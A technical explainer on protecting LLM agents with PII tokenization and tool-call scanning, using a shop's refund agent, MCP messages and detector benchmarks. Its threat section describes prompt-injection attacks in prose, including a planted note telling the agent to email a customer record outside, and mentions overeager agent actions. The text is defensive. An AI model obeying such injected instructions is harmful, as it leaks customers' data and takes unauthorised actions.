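# PII tokenization and tool-call scanning as runtime safeguards for LLM agents

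## How an agent reads data and calls tools

A large language model (LLM) takes in text and produces text. An LLM agent is an LLM run in a loop with tools, which are software functions for looking up a record, paying out money or sending an email. These tools let the model's output change things outside the conversation. An agent that deals with customers or staff constantly reads personally identifiable information (PII), such as names, email addresses and national identity numbers. Some of its actions, such as payments, are hard to undo.

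A model reaches databases and mail servers only through an ordinary program, so engineers can add two safeguards that work while the agent runs. PII tokenization replaces each personal value with a placeholder, such as `[EMAIL_1]`, before the text reaches the model. A protected store called the vault records which value each placeholder stands for, and software restores the real value when a permitted tool needs it. In tool-call scanning, a scanner inspects each action the model proposes before it happens, and allows it, blocks it or sends it to a person.

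### The agent loop

That program is the harness. Anthropic's *How tool use works* describes a cycle in which the model emits a structured request, the application's code carries out the operation, and the result goes back into the conversation. For a few tools, such as web search, Anthropic's servers run the code instead. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the same cycle for Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The harness first assembles a prompt from standing instructions, tool definitions and the user's message, and sends it to the model. The model returns either a final message for the user or a tool call, which names a tool and gives its arguments. If the model returns a tool call, the harness runs the tool, appends the call and its result to the prompt, and queries the model again. The cycle repeats until the model returns a message with no tool call.

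Take an online shop whose agent answers support tickets. The agent has three tools: `crm.lookup` fetches a record from the shop's customer database, `refund.issue` pays money back on an order, and `email.send` sends a message to an address. The shop's standing instructions permit refunds of up to 100 euros on goods that arrived damaged. A ticket comes in from Maria Keller, maria.keller@example.com, who writes that the kettle in order 48213 has a cracked lid and that she wants her money back. The model's first output is a call to look up the order. The harness passes it on in the format of the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting agents to tools, here without some of the required metadata:

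```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 7,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "crm.lookup",
    "arguments": { "order": "48213" }
  }
}
```

The tool returns a result with the same `id`, which ties it to the call:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 7,
  "result": {
    "resultType": "complete",
    "content": [
      {
        "type": "text",
        "text": "Maria Keller, maria.keller@example.com. Order 48213: kettle, EUR 62.50, delivered."
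      }
    ],
    "isError": false
  }
}
```

That text is now added to the model's context, the text from which it generates its next output. The model then outputs a call to `refund.issue` for 62.50 euros. After the confirmation arrives, it outputs a call to `email.send` with Keller's address and a short apology. On the fourth query, the model returns a closing message and the loop ends.

By that time the harness has sent Keller's ticket to the model four times and her customer record three times. Bolin explains that every Codex query contains the whole conversation so far. OpenAI's API lets a query refer to an earlier response instead, but Codex doesn't use this feature, partly to accommodate customers who have arranged for OpenAI not to retain their data. An agent may make hundreds of tool calls in a single turn, and each query resends any personal data that entered at the start. The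 model also has to copy values from one tool to the next. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* describes an agent that attaches a meeting transcript from Google Drive to a sales record. The full transcript passes through the model twice, once as the result of one call and once as an argument of the next. Keller's email address also passes through the model twice on its way from `crm.lookup` to `email.send`.

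### What MCP standardizes

Before Anthropic launched MCP in November 2024, connecting an agent to a tool generally took a custom integration for each pair. MCP standardizes the messages between the agent and a tool server. The server, such as one in front of the shop's customer database, responds to a `tools/list` request with each tool's name, description and expected arguments. A `tools/call` request runs one tool, and the server returns the result in a standard format with an error flag.

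In the Model Context Protocol (MCP), the application that contains the harness is called the host. According to the protocol's website, the host keeps the full conversation history, and a server receives only the context it needs. The shop's mail server receives the recipient and text of the message but has no access to the customer database. Apart from the model's provider, only the host has the whole exchange, so it is the natural place for both safeguards.

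The Model Context Protocol (MCP) supplies neither PII tokenization nor tool-call scanning. Its overview leaves each application to decide how to use its model and manage the context. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) recommends that a person always be able to refuse a tool call, and that client software show the arguments to the user before sending them, validate results before the model receives them and keep a log. These are "should" clauses, so an implementer can skip them. The binding "must" clauses require servers to validate their inputs and control access, and client software to distrust a tool's annotations, which describe how the tool behaves, unless they come from a trusted server.

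The 28 July 2026 version of the Model Context Protocol puts the tool's name in an HTTP header, so a network gateway can allow or refuse a call without reading the message body (Model Context Protocol, 2026). A gateway could forbid `refund.issue` outright, but it could not use the headers alone to tell a refund of 62.50 euros from one of 6,250 euros unless the server's developer had chosen to copy the amount into a header too. The specification permits such copying for some types of argument but warns against it for personal data, because intermediaries on the network can read the headers.

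### Where a safeguard can act

A safeguard can act at six points on this loop.

| Point | What passes there | PII tokenization | Tool-call scanning |
|---|---|---|---|
| User input | Keller's ticket | Replaces her name and address before the first query | Can use the ticket as evidence of what she asked for |
| Tool result | The record from `crm.lookup` | Replaces personal values before the record enters the context | No verdict here, though a separate filter can look for planted instructions |
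| Model output | The closing message | Restores values in text meant for a permitted reader | No verdict on prose |
| Tool call | A refund amount, an email recipient | Restores the real value if the tool may have it | Gives its verdict before the harness runs the call |
| Log | Copies of prompts, calls and results | Keeps real values out of the copies | Adds its verdicts to the record |
| Memory | Summaries and files that outlast a query | Keeps placeholders in the stored text | Sees only the later calls to which stored text leads |

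Both safeguards act on the tool call, so their order matters. If the scanner runs before restoration, it sees an email addressed to `[EMAIL_1]` and cannot tell whose address it is without help from the vault. Running it after restoration lets it read the real address, but if the scanner is a model on another company's servers, that company also receives the address.

Memory is hard to filter. Bolin writes that when a conversation grows too long for the model, Codex replaces it with a shorter list of items, including an encrypted summary that OpenAI's servers produce. If a customer's name was in the conversation before the replacement, it may remain in that summary, where no filter in the harness can detect it. Tokenization therefore has to happen before the data enters the conversation.

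Practitioners put their controls at much the same points. Help Net Security's *Your AI agent's system prompt is not a security control* summarizes guidance from Gee Rittenhouse of Amazon Web Services and Eric Johnson of the SANS Institute, a security training organisation. They recommend filtering data before it reaches the model, redacting PII from the output and checking each tool call against a policy. They don't consider instructions to the model a control, since someone can persuade the model to ignore them.

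### What can go wrong

Personal data can leak even when the loop works as its designers intended. Maria Keller's name and address go to the model's provider with every query, and into whatever logs the shop keeps. David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, advises developers in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection* to log enough to spot suspicious activity, potentially including everything the model reads and writes. Rittenhouse and Johnson want every prompt, tool call and response kept in storage that nobody can alter. Investigators need such records after an incident, but the records are also a second copy of customers' data, and the shop cannot easily erase a customer from them.

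The remaining harms are actions, and Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* sorts them by cause. In an honest mistake, the agent misjudges what an action will affect, such as when it treats a shared resource as a test copy. The support agent would make this kind of mistake if the shop had two customers called Maria Keller and it refunded the wrong one. In an overeager action, the agent understands the goal but goes further than the user authorized. Anthropic keeps a log of such incidents with its own coding agent. The logged incidents include uploading an engineer's access credential to an internal computing cluster and attempting changes to a live database. The support agent would be overeager in a milder way if it also refunded Keller's two previous orders to make up for the trouble. The two categories can be hard to tell apart. Anthropic counts one deletion of remote code branches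 as overeager, although it began with a misread instruction.

Prompt injection is text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions. In direct injection, the attacker writes to the agent himself, as a customer might by claiming in a ticket that the refund limit no longer applies. In indirect injection, the instruction arrives in other content that the agent reads. Suppose a stranger wrote to the shop quoting order 48213, and the shop's software filed his message among the notes on Keller's record. If he included an instruction to email the full record to an outside address, `crm.lookup` returns that instruction along with her details, and a model that follows it will call `email.send`. This attack requires neither access to the agent nor any unusual action by Keller.

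Anthropic lists one more cause, a model that pursues its own goal, and observes that the defence against every cause is to block the action.

Practitioners regard prompt injection as the worst of these dangers. SC Media's *OWASP updates top 10 security risks for LLM applications* reports that the Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit that publishes lists of software risks, ranked it first in its 2026 list for LLM applications, ahead of sensitive information disclosure and excessive agency. The OWASP GenAI Security Project (2026) based that edition partly on research into thousands of real-world incidents. However, Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* reports that relatively few recorded incidents involve prompt injection, so the ranking probably reflects what practitioners expect more than the damage recorded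 so far. Microsoft concludes from OWASP's separate list for agents that an agent's failures are usually bad outcomes rather than bad text, and that they happen because the agent can mistake untrusted content for an instruction and act on it with delegated authority.

### Why a model cannot reliably tell data from instructions

Earlier systems also mixed data with commands. Schneier (2024), in *LLMs' Data-Control Path Insecurity*, gives the example of the telephone network, which once carried control signals on the same channel as voices, so a caller could operate the switch by whistling into the phone. The fix, a standard by the 1980s, was to send commands on a separate channel. Databases had a similar problem with SQL injection, where an attacker types a database command into a field on a web page. Parameterised queries prevent this by passing the input strictly as a value, which the database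 engine never interprets as a command.

David C argues that such a remedy cannot be applied to language models. A model receives a single sequence of tokens (units of text, unrelated to PII tokenization) and predicts the next one. The shop's instructions, Keller's complaint and the stranger's note are all parts of that sequence. He gives the example of a recruiter's system instructed to score CVs. If a candidate hides a sentence in his CV telling the system to approve him for interview, the model may treat it as part of its instructions.

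The parts of a prompt carry labels. In OpenAI's interface, each item has a role, such as developer or user, which indicates how much weight its content should have, as Bolin notes. Developers can also train a model to prioritize its instructions over anything in the data that resembles an instruction, or mark off outside text with tags. David C accepts that such techniques make an attack harder, but objects that they impose a distinction between instructions and data on a technology that does not inherently make it. Training gives the model a tendency to respect the labels, but an attacker can keep rephrasing until some wording overcomes that tendency. How often this succeeds has to be measured.

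David C therefore proposes treating the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". In security, a confused deputy is a privileged program that someone without its privileges manipulates into acting for them. The stranger cannot look up customers or issue refunds, but could get the agent to do so. The worst case to plan for is therefore an attacker who can use the agent's tools directly. David C wants designers to rely more on conventional code that limits what the system can do than on keeping hostile text away from the model.

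Rittenhouse and Johnson, in guidance that Help Net Security covers, find that risk concentrates where one agent combines sensitive data, untrusted content and a way to communicate with the outside. The support agent is in this high-risk position because it reads the customer database and the tickets and can call `email.send`. The shop could hardly remove any of these and still have the agent do its job.

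### Confidentiality and integrity

Two terms from computer security, confidentiality and integrity, help distinguish what the safeguards do. Confidentiality concerns who learns a value, for example whether Maria Keller's address stays with the shop or reaches the model's provider, a log or a stranger. Integrity, for an agent, concerns which actions happen, for example whether the shop refunds the right order, only once, and for an amount its rules permit.

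PII tokenization addresses confidentiality. In the design Anthropic sketches, the software connecting the agent to its tools replaces personal values with tokens before the model receives them and restores them for the next tool, so the real values never pass through the model. Tokenization doesn't make the agent's actions correct, since an injected instruction to refund order 48213 twice works just as well when the record names the customer as `[NAME_1]`.

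Tool-call scanning mainly protects integrity, since the scanner either allows or blocks the second refund. It can also protect confidentiality, because blocking the email to the stranger keeps him from seeing Keller's record. But without tokenization, the model's provider received that record as soon as `crm.lookup` returned it, one step before the agent tried to send the email.

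## Finding personal data in text

Before software can replace Maria Keller's address with a placeholder, a detector has to find the address. The detector takes a text and returns spans (start and end positions), each with a type such as person or phone number. Recall is the share of the personal values in the text that the detector finds. Precision is the share of the returned spans that are personal data. Any value the detector misses goes to the model as plain text, so recall limits what PII tokenization can protect.

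### Patterns and checksums

The simplest detectors are regular expressions, which describe the shape of a string. An email address is a run of permitted characters, an @ sign and a domain, and a pattern for that shape finds `maria.keller@example.com` in any sentence. Patterns are fast and easy to inspect, but they cannot find names, because "Maria Keller" has the same shape as "Baker Street".

Numbers do have a shape, but different kinds of number share it. Sixteen digits in a support ticket could be a payment card or a parcel's tracking code. A checksum settles most such cases. Card issuers choose the last digit of a card number so that the whole number passes the Luhn check, and the detector described in Microsoft's *Credit card number* accepts only strings of 14 to 19 digits that pass it. The check doubles every second digit, counting from the right, subtracts 9 from any result above 9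 and adds everything up. The total must be a multiple of 10. Here is the check on 4095-2609-9393-4932, an example from the documentation of Presidio, an open-source detection framework that began at Microsoft:

```
Digits     4  0  9  5  2  6  0  9  9  3  9  3  4  9  3  2
Doubled    8    18     4     0    18    18     8     6
Counted    8  0  9  5  4  6  0  9  9  3  9  3  8  9  6  2
```

The bottom row adds up to 90, so the number is valid. If the final digit were 3 instead of 2, the total would be 91 and the number would fail. About one in ten random strings of digits passes by chance, so the check removes roughly 90% of the false alarms from tracking codes and similar numbers.

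Requiring a valid checksum also causes misses. A customer who mistypes one digit of her card number has still disclosed the other fifteen, but the number fails the check and stays in the text. Hsu and Berlin (2026), in *Broad and Efficient PII Detection with Unified Labels*, built a detector at Cisco that marks anything the text presents as a card number and leaves the checksum to a later step. Such a detector has to consider the surrounding words.

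### Models that use the surrounding words

Developers train a named-entity recognizer on annotated text, often news, to mark the names of people, organisations and places. Presidio by default uses the recognizer in spaCy, an open-source language library. It can find "Keller" in a sentence that wasn't in its training data, because the neighbouring words suggest a person. It has no category for bank account or health-service numbers, and it doesn't distinguish a customer's name from a famous author's.

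A token classifier trained for privacy covers both names and numbers. OpenAI (2026) released one, Privacy Filter, in April with a model card. It detects eight types of data: private persons, addresses, email addresses, phone numbers, URLs, dates, account numbers, and secrets such as passwords. The model reads the text once and gives every token a probability for each of 33 classes. One class means "not personal". The other 32 combine the eight types with four positions, since a token can begin a span, continue it, end it or be the whole span. If "Maria" and "Keller" are one token each, their correct classes are "begins a person" and "ends a person". A decoding step then picks the most probable valid sequence of classes, so that no span ends before it has begun. Operators can adjust this step to mark more text or less.

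Each layer of Privacy Filter covers only 128 tokens on either side of the token being labelled. In one of OpenAI's tests, a writer said that "marigold" would stand for an account number and gave the number much later. Recall fell as the distance between the two grew. Unusual formats also reduced recall, to 0.67 when the test texts spelled digits out as words and to 0.63 when they broke values up with odd spacing. OpenAI warns that the model may miss uncommon names, initials and regional naming conventions.

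The eight types are fixed unless someone retrains the model. GLiNER, a family of general span extractors, takes the names of the types at run time, so the shop could add "loyalty card number" without any training. The model scores candidate stretches of text against each name. Hsu and Berlin note that popular versions process the type descriptions again with every input, so a more careful description makes every request slower. GLiNER Guard, a set of models from this family for English and Russian, has a variant that encodes the descriptions once and stores the result, though its deployed pipeline still finds phone and tax numbers with rules. Models that accept new types can still miss much of the personal data in a text. *GLiNER2-PII* (2026) reports recall of 0.72 and 0.68 on legal and medical texts for a new model trained for personal data, against 0.31 to 0.43 for three earlier GLiNER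 models, in a test run by the new model's developers.

### How Presidio combines detectors

Presidio runs several recognizers over the same text and gives each finding a confidence score. Microsoft's *The Presidio-analyzer decision process* shows the scores for a message in which someone named Bart Simpson gives his name, the card number above and a phone number. The card pattern starts at 0.3 because many digit strings fit it, and the score rises to 1.0 when the number passes the checksum. The phone pattern starts at 0.5, and the word "phone" just before the number raises it to 0.85. The name has no pattern to match, so spaCy's recognizer finds the name and scores it 0.85. The operator sets the minimum score for a finding to count. With a cut-off of 0.6, the same phone number would stay in the text if the word "phone" were not beside it.

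Microsoft also lets operators add their own recognizers and deny lists of fixed words. A shop could write a recognizer for its customer numbers in a few lines of code.

The combined system keeps the strengths and weaknesses of its parts. *Mind the Gap* (2026) compared Presidio's results on familiar and unfamiliar text. Presidio found every US Social Security number and IP address in both, but its overall recall fell from 0.89 to 0.78 on the unfamiliar text while its precision barely changed, so the losses were in types without a fixed format. Fixed formats help only when people follow them. In the benchmark *REDACT* (2026), Presidio found 2% of values that the writer gave only in part and 7% of values in disguised form. Microsoft warns that the record of scores shows why Presidio detected a value, but not why it missed one.

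### Five tools on whole documents

Developers usually test detectors on single sentences or short messages, often from data they published themselves. *Reversible Pseudonymisation of Documents Sent to External LLMs* (Beskorovainyi, 2026) tests five open tools on documents in Russian and UK English: Presidio, Privacy Filter, GLiNER Guard, Prompt Anonymizer (built on Presidio) and pii-guard, which combines rules and a token classifier for Russian. The baseline is a set of patterns with checksums.

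He wrote down four thresholds before running any tool. A tool should find at least 99% of structured identifiers, such as passport, health-service and card numbers, and at least 95% of names, addresses and organisations. It should leave a value visible in at most 2% of texts. The fourth threshold was for replacing placeholders with the original values after a model answers, and his own engine later missed it on Russian names. A tool met a threshold only if the whole 95% confidence interval for its result did.

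The first round used public datasets, and no tool was judged on data from its own developers. This rule made a difference for GLiNER Guard, which found 87.1% of the structured identifiers in its developers' Russian benchmark, described in *GLiNER Guard* (2026), but 70.8% in another Russian dataset. No existing tool met every threshold. GLiNER Guard came closest in UK English, where it found 96.4% of identifiers but left a visible value in 4.0% of the texts.

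For the second round Beskorovainyi wrote a program that generates contracts, certificates, business letters, personnel files and hospital discharge summaries. It made 1,000 documents per language for the final test. It added typos and odd number formats to about four in ten of them, and in those it wrote some identifiers in words, with dots or with a wrong digit. The best existing tools left a whole value visible in 61% of the Russian documents (pii-guard) and 58% of the UK documents (GLiNER Guard). His own engine, pii-roundtrip, did so in 0.3% and 0.2%. The UK results were:

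| Tool | Documents with a whole value visible | Documents with any part of a value visible | Recall, identifiers | Recall, names, addresses, organisations | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| pii-roundtrip | 0.2% | 0.2% | 100.0% | 99.98% | 99.8% |
| GLiNER Guard | 58.3% | 83.5% | 95.4% | 88.9% | 94.8% |
| Presidio | 61.1% | 100.0% | 92.5% | 58.5% | 79.0% |
| Privacy Filter | 81.1% | 96.8% | 95.7% | 84.4% | 92.9% |
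| Prompt Anonymizer | 100.0% | 100.0% | 68.1% | 51.5% | 99.0% |
| Pattern baseline | 100.0% | 100.0% | 90.7% | 0.0% | 100.0% |

The first column is the more lenient measure because it ignores partly masked addresses, such as one where the tool masked the postcode but not the town. It also penalises tools that detect fewer types of data. For example, Privacy Filter has no organisation type. If organisations were not counted, it would leave a whole value visible in 33.0% of UK documents, fewer than GLiNER Guard.

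The engine runs two existing models, GLiNER Guard and, for Russian, pii-guard, and adds rules. These rules recognise identifiers by their checksums, read numbers written in words, and extend partly detected addresses to their full length. The most useful idea for an agent is probably propagation, which means that once the engine finds a name in a document, it masks that name throughout. GLiNER Guard alone would sometimes mask a full name in the first paragraph and miss the same person in the signature.

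Beskorovainyi published the documents, the judging rules and a promise to report the outcome before he ran any tool on this last set, so he did not get the 0.2% by picking a favourable test. But he built both the engine and the program that generates the documents. The two share checksum code, which makes the perfect score on identifiers "close to circular", as he writes. He had also improved the engine over six earlier sets from that program, while he ran the other tools with their documented defaults and did not tune them.

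His results suggest that the engine's lead is smaller on other people's data. Of 553 UK identifiers from a public NVIDIA dataset, the engine found 552 and GLiNER Guard found 548. The engine's recall for names, addresses and organisations was 98.3% on the NVIDIA texts, compared with 99.98% on his own documents. He did not test any real documents.

### Why long documents leak

A tool can find 95% of identifiers and still fail on most documents, and much of the reason is arithmetic. Suppose a detector catches each value with probability r, independently of the others. It catches all n values in a document with probability rⁿ, so the document leaks with probability

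1 − rⁿ

Beskorovainyi's UK documents hold about 26 values each. At a recall of 0.99, the chance of catching all 26 is 0.99²⁶, or about 0.77, so about 23% of these documents leak at least one value. A short message with one value leaks 1% of the time at the same recall. To limit leaks to 2% of documents with 26 values, recall must be at least the 26th root of 0.98, or about 0.9992, which allows one miss in roughly 1,300 values.

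The 2% threshold is thus far stricter than the two recall thresholds beside it. About half of the 26 values are identifiers, and the rest are names, addresses or organisations. A tool that only just met the recall thresholds, with 99% on the identifiers and 95% on the rest, would by the same formula leave at least part of a value visible in about 55% of documents. Even the engine's 98.3% recall on NVIDIA's texts would mean a leak in about one in five documents with 13 names and addresses each. The risk is greater for an agent, because misses accumulate over everything it reads in a session. If it works through a hundred customer records with three values each, a recall of 99% gives a 95% chance of at least one miss.

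Real misses cluster, though, rather than occurring independently, because the conditions that cause a detector to miss values usually affect a whole document. GLiNER Guard left a whole value visible in 38.3% of the UK documents without added noise and in 86.0% of the noisy ones. Misses also cluster by person. If a detector fails to recognise an unusual surname once, it will probably fail again in the next paragraph and the next ticket.

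When missed values cluster in the same documents, fewer documents leak at a given recall, but each leaking document exposes more values. For example, a detector with a recall of 0.99 would miss 260 values across 1,000 documents with 26 values each. If the misses were independent, they would affect about 230 documents. If the detector instead missed every value on one unfamiliar form and none elsewhere, ten documents would leak all 26 of their values. GLiNER Guard's misses are much closer to the independent case. Based on its recall on the UK documents, the formula predicts that 88% of them would show at least part of a value, and the measured figure was 83.5%.

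Clustering also makes tests less informative than they look. Ten thousand values from a few hundred similar documents may contain no example of the form that the detector misses. Beskorovainyi therefore computed confidence intervals for recall by resampling whole documents instead of single values. An average can also hide a worse problem for a shop, which is that the same few customers are exposed every time they write.

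### Tests on other texts

Independent evaluations confirm that accuracy depends heavily on the kind of text. Uppala (2026), in *OpenAI Privacy Filter*, tested that model on 32 datasets in 14 languages and compared it on many of them with Presidio, a GLiNER model and OpenAI's general model GPT-4o. The main measure was F1, which combines precision and recall into one number between 0 and 1. On general synthetic data, Privacy Filter led with 0.86, against 0.58 for GLiNER and 0.43 for Presidio. On medical questions, it fell to 0.46 and GPT-4o led with 0.70. Uppala included GPT-4o only as an upper bound. A shop trying to keep names away from outside models could hardly use it, because GPT-4o is itself an outside model.

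The customer-support messages in that evaluation are the most similar to Keller's ticket. On the English messages, Privacy Filter scored 0.98 on email addresses and 0.92 on phone numbers, but 0.39 on names and 0.30 on postal addresses. These scores somewhat overstate how much personal data would be exposed, because Uppala counted a span only if both ends were exactly right. A detector that marked "Ms Keller" where the dataset had "Keller" was counted as missing the name, even though it had hidden it.

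Uppala's near-zero scores for Persian and Ukrainian require even more caution. They come from general texts in which many of the people are presumably public figures, and OpenAI trained Privacy Filter to mark private persons. Privacy Filter found 74% of names, addresses and organisations in Beskorovainyi's Russian documents, which are in Cyrillic script, as Ukrainian is.

Nearly all of this text is synthetic. *Data Quality in RVL-CDIP* (Larson and Leach, 2026) instead used real scanned pages that American tobacco companies had to release in litigation. Larson and Leach ran four detectors on 1,773 hand-annotated pages. Of the pages with a Social Security number, Presidio caught 97%, Google's service 93%, Amazon's 77% and Microsoft Azure's 70%. Social Security numbers are supposedly easy to detect because they have a fixed format. The annotators recorded eleven sensitive types, seven of which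 none of the tools could detect. The tools also could not tell a home address from an employer's. Larson and Leach gave up on automatic detection and had people annotate the whole collection.

Hospital notes show the same gap in coverage. *MedDeID enables locally governed clinical-text de-identification from real or synthetic training data* (2026) found that OpenAI's Privacy Filter recognised 12.6% of the text naming healthcare organisations and none of the professions. The detector has no type for either, so an operator could have predicted this from its documentation. Operators should compare a detector's list of types with the data they hold before choosing it.

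### The cost of masking too much

An operator can raise recall by lowering the score a finding needs to count, but this causes more false alarms. On clinical notes, *Towards Fair and Efficient De-identification* (2026) measured a recall of 0.91 and a precision of 0.61 for Presidio, so nearly four in ten of the words it masked did not need masking. BERT, an older and much smaller language model, reached 0.99 on both measures after training on such notes. In Uppala's customer-support messages, more than half of the spans Privacy Filter returned did not match a labelled value.

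Every false alarm removes something the agent may need. In a small test with the samples that ship with Privacy Filter, *Locale-Conditioned Few-Shot Prompting Mitigates Demonstration Regurgitation in On-Device PII Substitution* (2026) found that dates accounted for 44.5% of the false alarms. If the shop refunded goods only within thirty days of delivery, the model could not apply that rule with the delivery date masked. A masked order number does less harm as long as the harness can restore it in the call to `crm.lookup`. Over-masking rarely destroys data permanently because the vault keeps the original, but nobody can take back a name that has gone to the provider. This is a reason to favour recall over precision until the agent starts to make mistakes because it lacks facts.

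Some apparent false alarms are disagreements about what counts as personal data. Hsu and Berlin relabelled a widely used dataset under stricter definitions. In five categories, including passport and card numbers, 59% to 86% of the examples labelled in either version were labelled only in the original. For example, the original labels marked a passport number in "Don't forget to bring your YV9022888!", although the sentence doesn't mention a passport. Another dataset, SPY, labels only the personal data of the person who wrote the text. OpenAI reports that Privacy Filter's precision on SPY rose from 0.41 to 0.96 after training on a tenth of SPY's training data, mostly because the model learned the dataset's definition. Published precision therefore predicts little about how a detector will perform for a shop with its own definition, and the shop has to measure precision on its own tickets.

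### Labelled fields

Many of the texts an agent reads come from databases, where personal data is easier to find because column names can identify it. Without a column called `phone`, a detector has to guess from context that ten digits are a phone number. OpenAI used simple sentences to test how much such clues help Privacy Filter. When words like "my home landline number" came just before the value, recall across all types was 0.86. It was 0.71 with the clue after the value and 0.58 with no clue. Recall for phone numbers fell from 0.92 to 0.32, while recall for email addresses, which have a recognizable format, stayed above 0.96 throughout. Similarly, Microsoft's Purview Data Map, a tool for cataloguing company data, applies its classifiers for person names, birth dates, email addresses and US phone numbers only to structured data such as tables.

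If `crm.lookup` returned Keller's record as labelled fields, the shop would need no detector for most of it:

```json
{
  "name": "Maria Keller",
  "email": "maria.keller@example.com",
  "order": "48213",
  "amount_eur": 62.50,
  "note": "Call her husband Tom on 0151 555 0123 if nobody answers."
}
```

The harness can replace the values in `name` and `email` and leave `order` and `amount_eur` unchanged. It doesn't have to estimate probabilities to do this, and it fails only when someone has typed a value into the wrong field. The `note` field is free text, so the shop still needs a detector to find Tom and his number there.

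The labelled fields can also help with free text. Once the harness has read "Maria Keller" in the record, it can search for that exact string in the note and in every later message, much as Beskorovainyi's engine does within a document. An exact search will find an unusual surname that no model recognises, but it will miss nicknames and different spellings such as "Mrs Keler".

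## Replacing a value with a placeholder

Once a detector has returned its spans, the harness has to put something in their place. Suppose the record from `crm.lookup` includes the line "Maria Keller, maria.keller@example.com. Call her husband Tom on 0151 555 0123." Here is that line under five methods, with fictitious replacement values:

| Method | What the model reads | Who can reverse it |
|---|---|---|
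| Deletion | [REDACTED], [REDACTED]. Call her husband [REDACTED] on [REDACTED]. | Nobody |
| Typed placeholder | [NAME_1], [EMAIL_1]. Call her husband [NAME_2] on [PHONE_1]. | Anyone who can read the vault |
| Random string | Xk81Qz, p7RmW2. Call her husband Vd40Ls on 9TnbH6. | Anyone who can read the vault |
| Surrogate | Ingrid Solberg, ingrid.solberg@example.net. Call her husband Paul on 0161 555 0148. | Anyone who can read the vault |
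| Format-preserving encryption | Tqxva Wmrkeo, qhtzo.vrwnai@example.com. Call her husband Zib on 7302 918 4465. | Anyone who has the key |

After deletion, the model can still infer that a kettle arrived damaged and that the shop owes a refund, but it cannot send the apology because it has no address to pass to `email.send`. If it enters "[REDACTED]" as the recipient, the harness cannot determine which of the four deleted values to use.

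A typed placeholder such as `[EMAIL_1]` lets the model see that the hidden value is an email address. The model can copy the placeholder into a tool call, and the harness can look up the real address. The harness can look up a random string such as `p7RmW2` just as easily, but the model has to guess from the context that it stands for an email address.

Surrogates are appealing because they read like ordinary text, but this also makes failed restoration harder to recognize. A customer who receives a letter addressed to `[NAME_1]` can see that something went wrong, while a letter addressed to the surrogate name Ingrid Solberg looks as if it was meant for someone else. Format-preserving encryption keeps a value's length and character types, so it suits a tool that accepts only eleven-digit phone numbers, but it turns names into gibberish.

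### What replacement costs the model

*On the Impact of Anonymization on the Performance of Large Language Models* (Deußer, Hahnbück and colleagues, 2026) compares several of these methods on GPT-4o mini, an older OpenAI model. On MuSR, a benchmark of multi-step reasoning over long texts, the model scored 0.73 with the original text and 0.70 with numbered placeholders such as `<LOC>-1`. It scored 0.58 when every city became `[CITY]`, and 0.52 when every value became the same marker. A MuSR text mentions about nine different entities a total of 67 times, and a model can hardly follow them if they all look alike. Random strings did about as well as numbered placeholders or slightly worse.

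The scoring exaggerates the gap somewhat because the evaluation script checks for the original names in the answer, and software can restore a name from a numbered placeholder like `<LOC>-1` but not from a generic marker. The small loss from numbered placeholders may not be real, since GPT-4o mini scored 0.70 with and without them in the main experiment.

That experiment covered five models and eleven benchmarks, and most scores fell by a few points. The exception was RGB, where the model has to answer from retrieved documents. GPT-4o mini's score fell from 0.80 to 0.32 there, and the other four models' scores fell by between 0.22 and 0.44. The shop's agent also answers from retrieved records and could be affected in the same way, but the anonymizer in the experiment replaced much more than personal data. It removed "Earth" and "Sun" from a question about eclipses, and both exchange rates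 from a question about whether the euro had risen. A shop that masks Keller's name but leaves the kettle, the price and the delivery date removes much less of what the model needs.

Deußer and colleagues also found that the more capable models lost more points when the text was anonymized. Qwen2.5-72B lost 6.9 points on average, while the much weaker Teuken-7B lost 2.3. However, Teuken's scores had less room to fall, since it scored almost zero on two benchmarks even with the original text. Telling GPT-4o mini that its input was anonymized made no consistent difference to its scores.

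Results from other tests differ on how much placeholders reduce usefulness. *Redakto* (2026) found no substantial loss in most cases. In *LLM-Redactor* (2026), a judge model preferred the answer to the unredacted prompt about 75–80% of the time. Those answers came from a model with only four billion parameters, and a preference rate doesn't measure how much worse the other answer was.

### A vault or a key

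There are two ways to make a replacement reversible. The first is to use a vault. The harness creates a new placeholder when it first encounters a value and stores the pair in the vault. `[EMAIL_1]` has no mathematical connection to Keller's address, so nobody can compute the address from the placeholder alone. But a thief who copies the vault gets every value in it, and if the shop loses the vault, nobody can restore the values. Beskorovainyi keeps the mapping for this kind of replacement on the user's own machine. The shop can also forget one person by deleting their row from the vault. If it deletes Keller's, `[EMAIL_1]` in the old logs no longer leads to her address.

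A keyed function computes the replacement from the value and a secret key. If the function is encryption, the shop can recover the value with the same key and needs no stored table. Two servers with the same key will produce the same replacement for a given value without communicating. But a leaked key exposes every value ever replaced with it, and the shop cannot make Keller's data unrecoverable without changing the key for everyone.

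A keyed hash such as HMAC lies between the two. It turns a value and a key into a fixed-length code that nobody can reverse, even with the key. It can produce the same surrogate for Keller every time, but restoring her name still requires a vault. Without a key, anyone could hash a list of known email addresses and look for matches.

### Format-preserving encryption

Ordinary encryption works on bits and doesn't preserve the format of its input. A US Social Security number has nine digits, but its encrypted form, read as a number, may have more and no longer fit the same field. Format-preserving encryption instead uses the key to select a permutation of all nine-digit strings, which maps each string to a unique nine-digit string.

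The main method is FF1, which Dworkin and Mouha (2025) specify for the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) in *Recommendation for Block Cipher Modes of Operation*. FF1 splits the input in two, so Tom's number, 01515550123, becomes 01515 and 550123. It feeds the second part and the key into a function built on AES, the standard block cipher, to get a large number. It adds that number to the first part and keeps the last five digits of the sum. If the large number ended in 83204, 01515 would become 84719. The parts then swap roles, so 84719 goes into the function and 550123 changes. After ten rounds, FF1 rejoins the parts.

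Decryption runs the rounds in reverse. Each round leaves one part unchanged, so anyone with the key can use that part to recompute the number added to the other part, then subtract it.

FF1 also takes a "tweak", an extra input that changes the permutation and need not be secret. Dworkin and Mouha give the example of a database of 100 million payment cards that encrypts only the middle six digits of each card number. About 100 cards share each combination of six digits. If every card has the same tweak, those cards also share a ciphertext, so anyone who learns the hidden digits of one learns them for the rest. If the tweak is the card's ten visible digits, the 100 ciphertexts will almost certainly differ.

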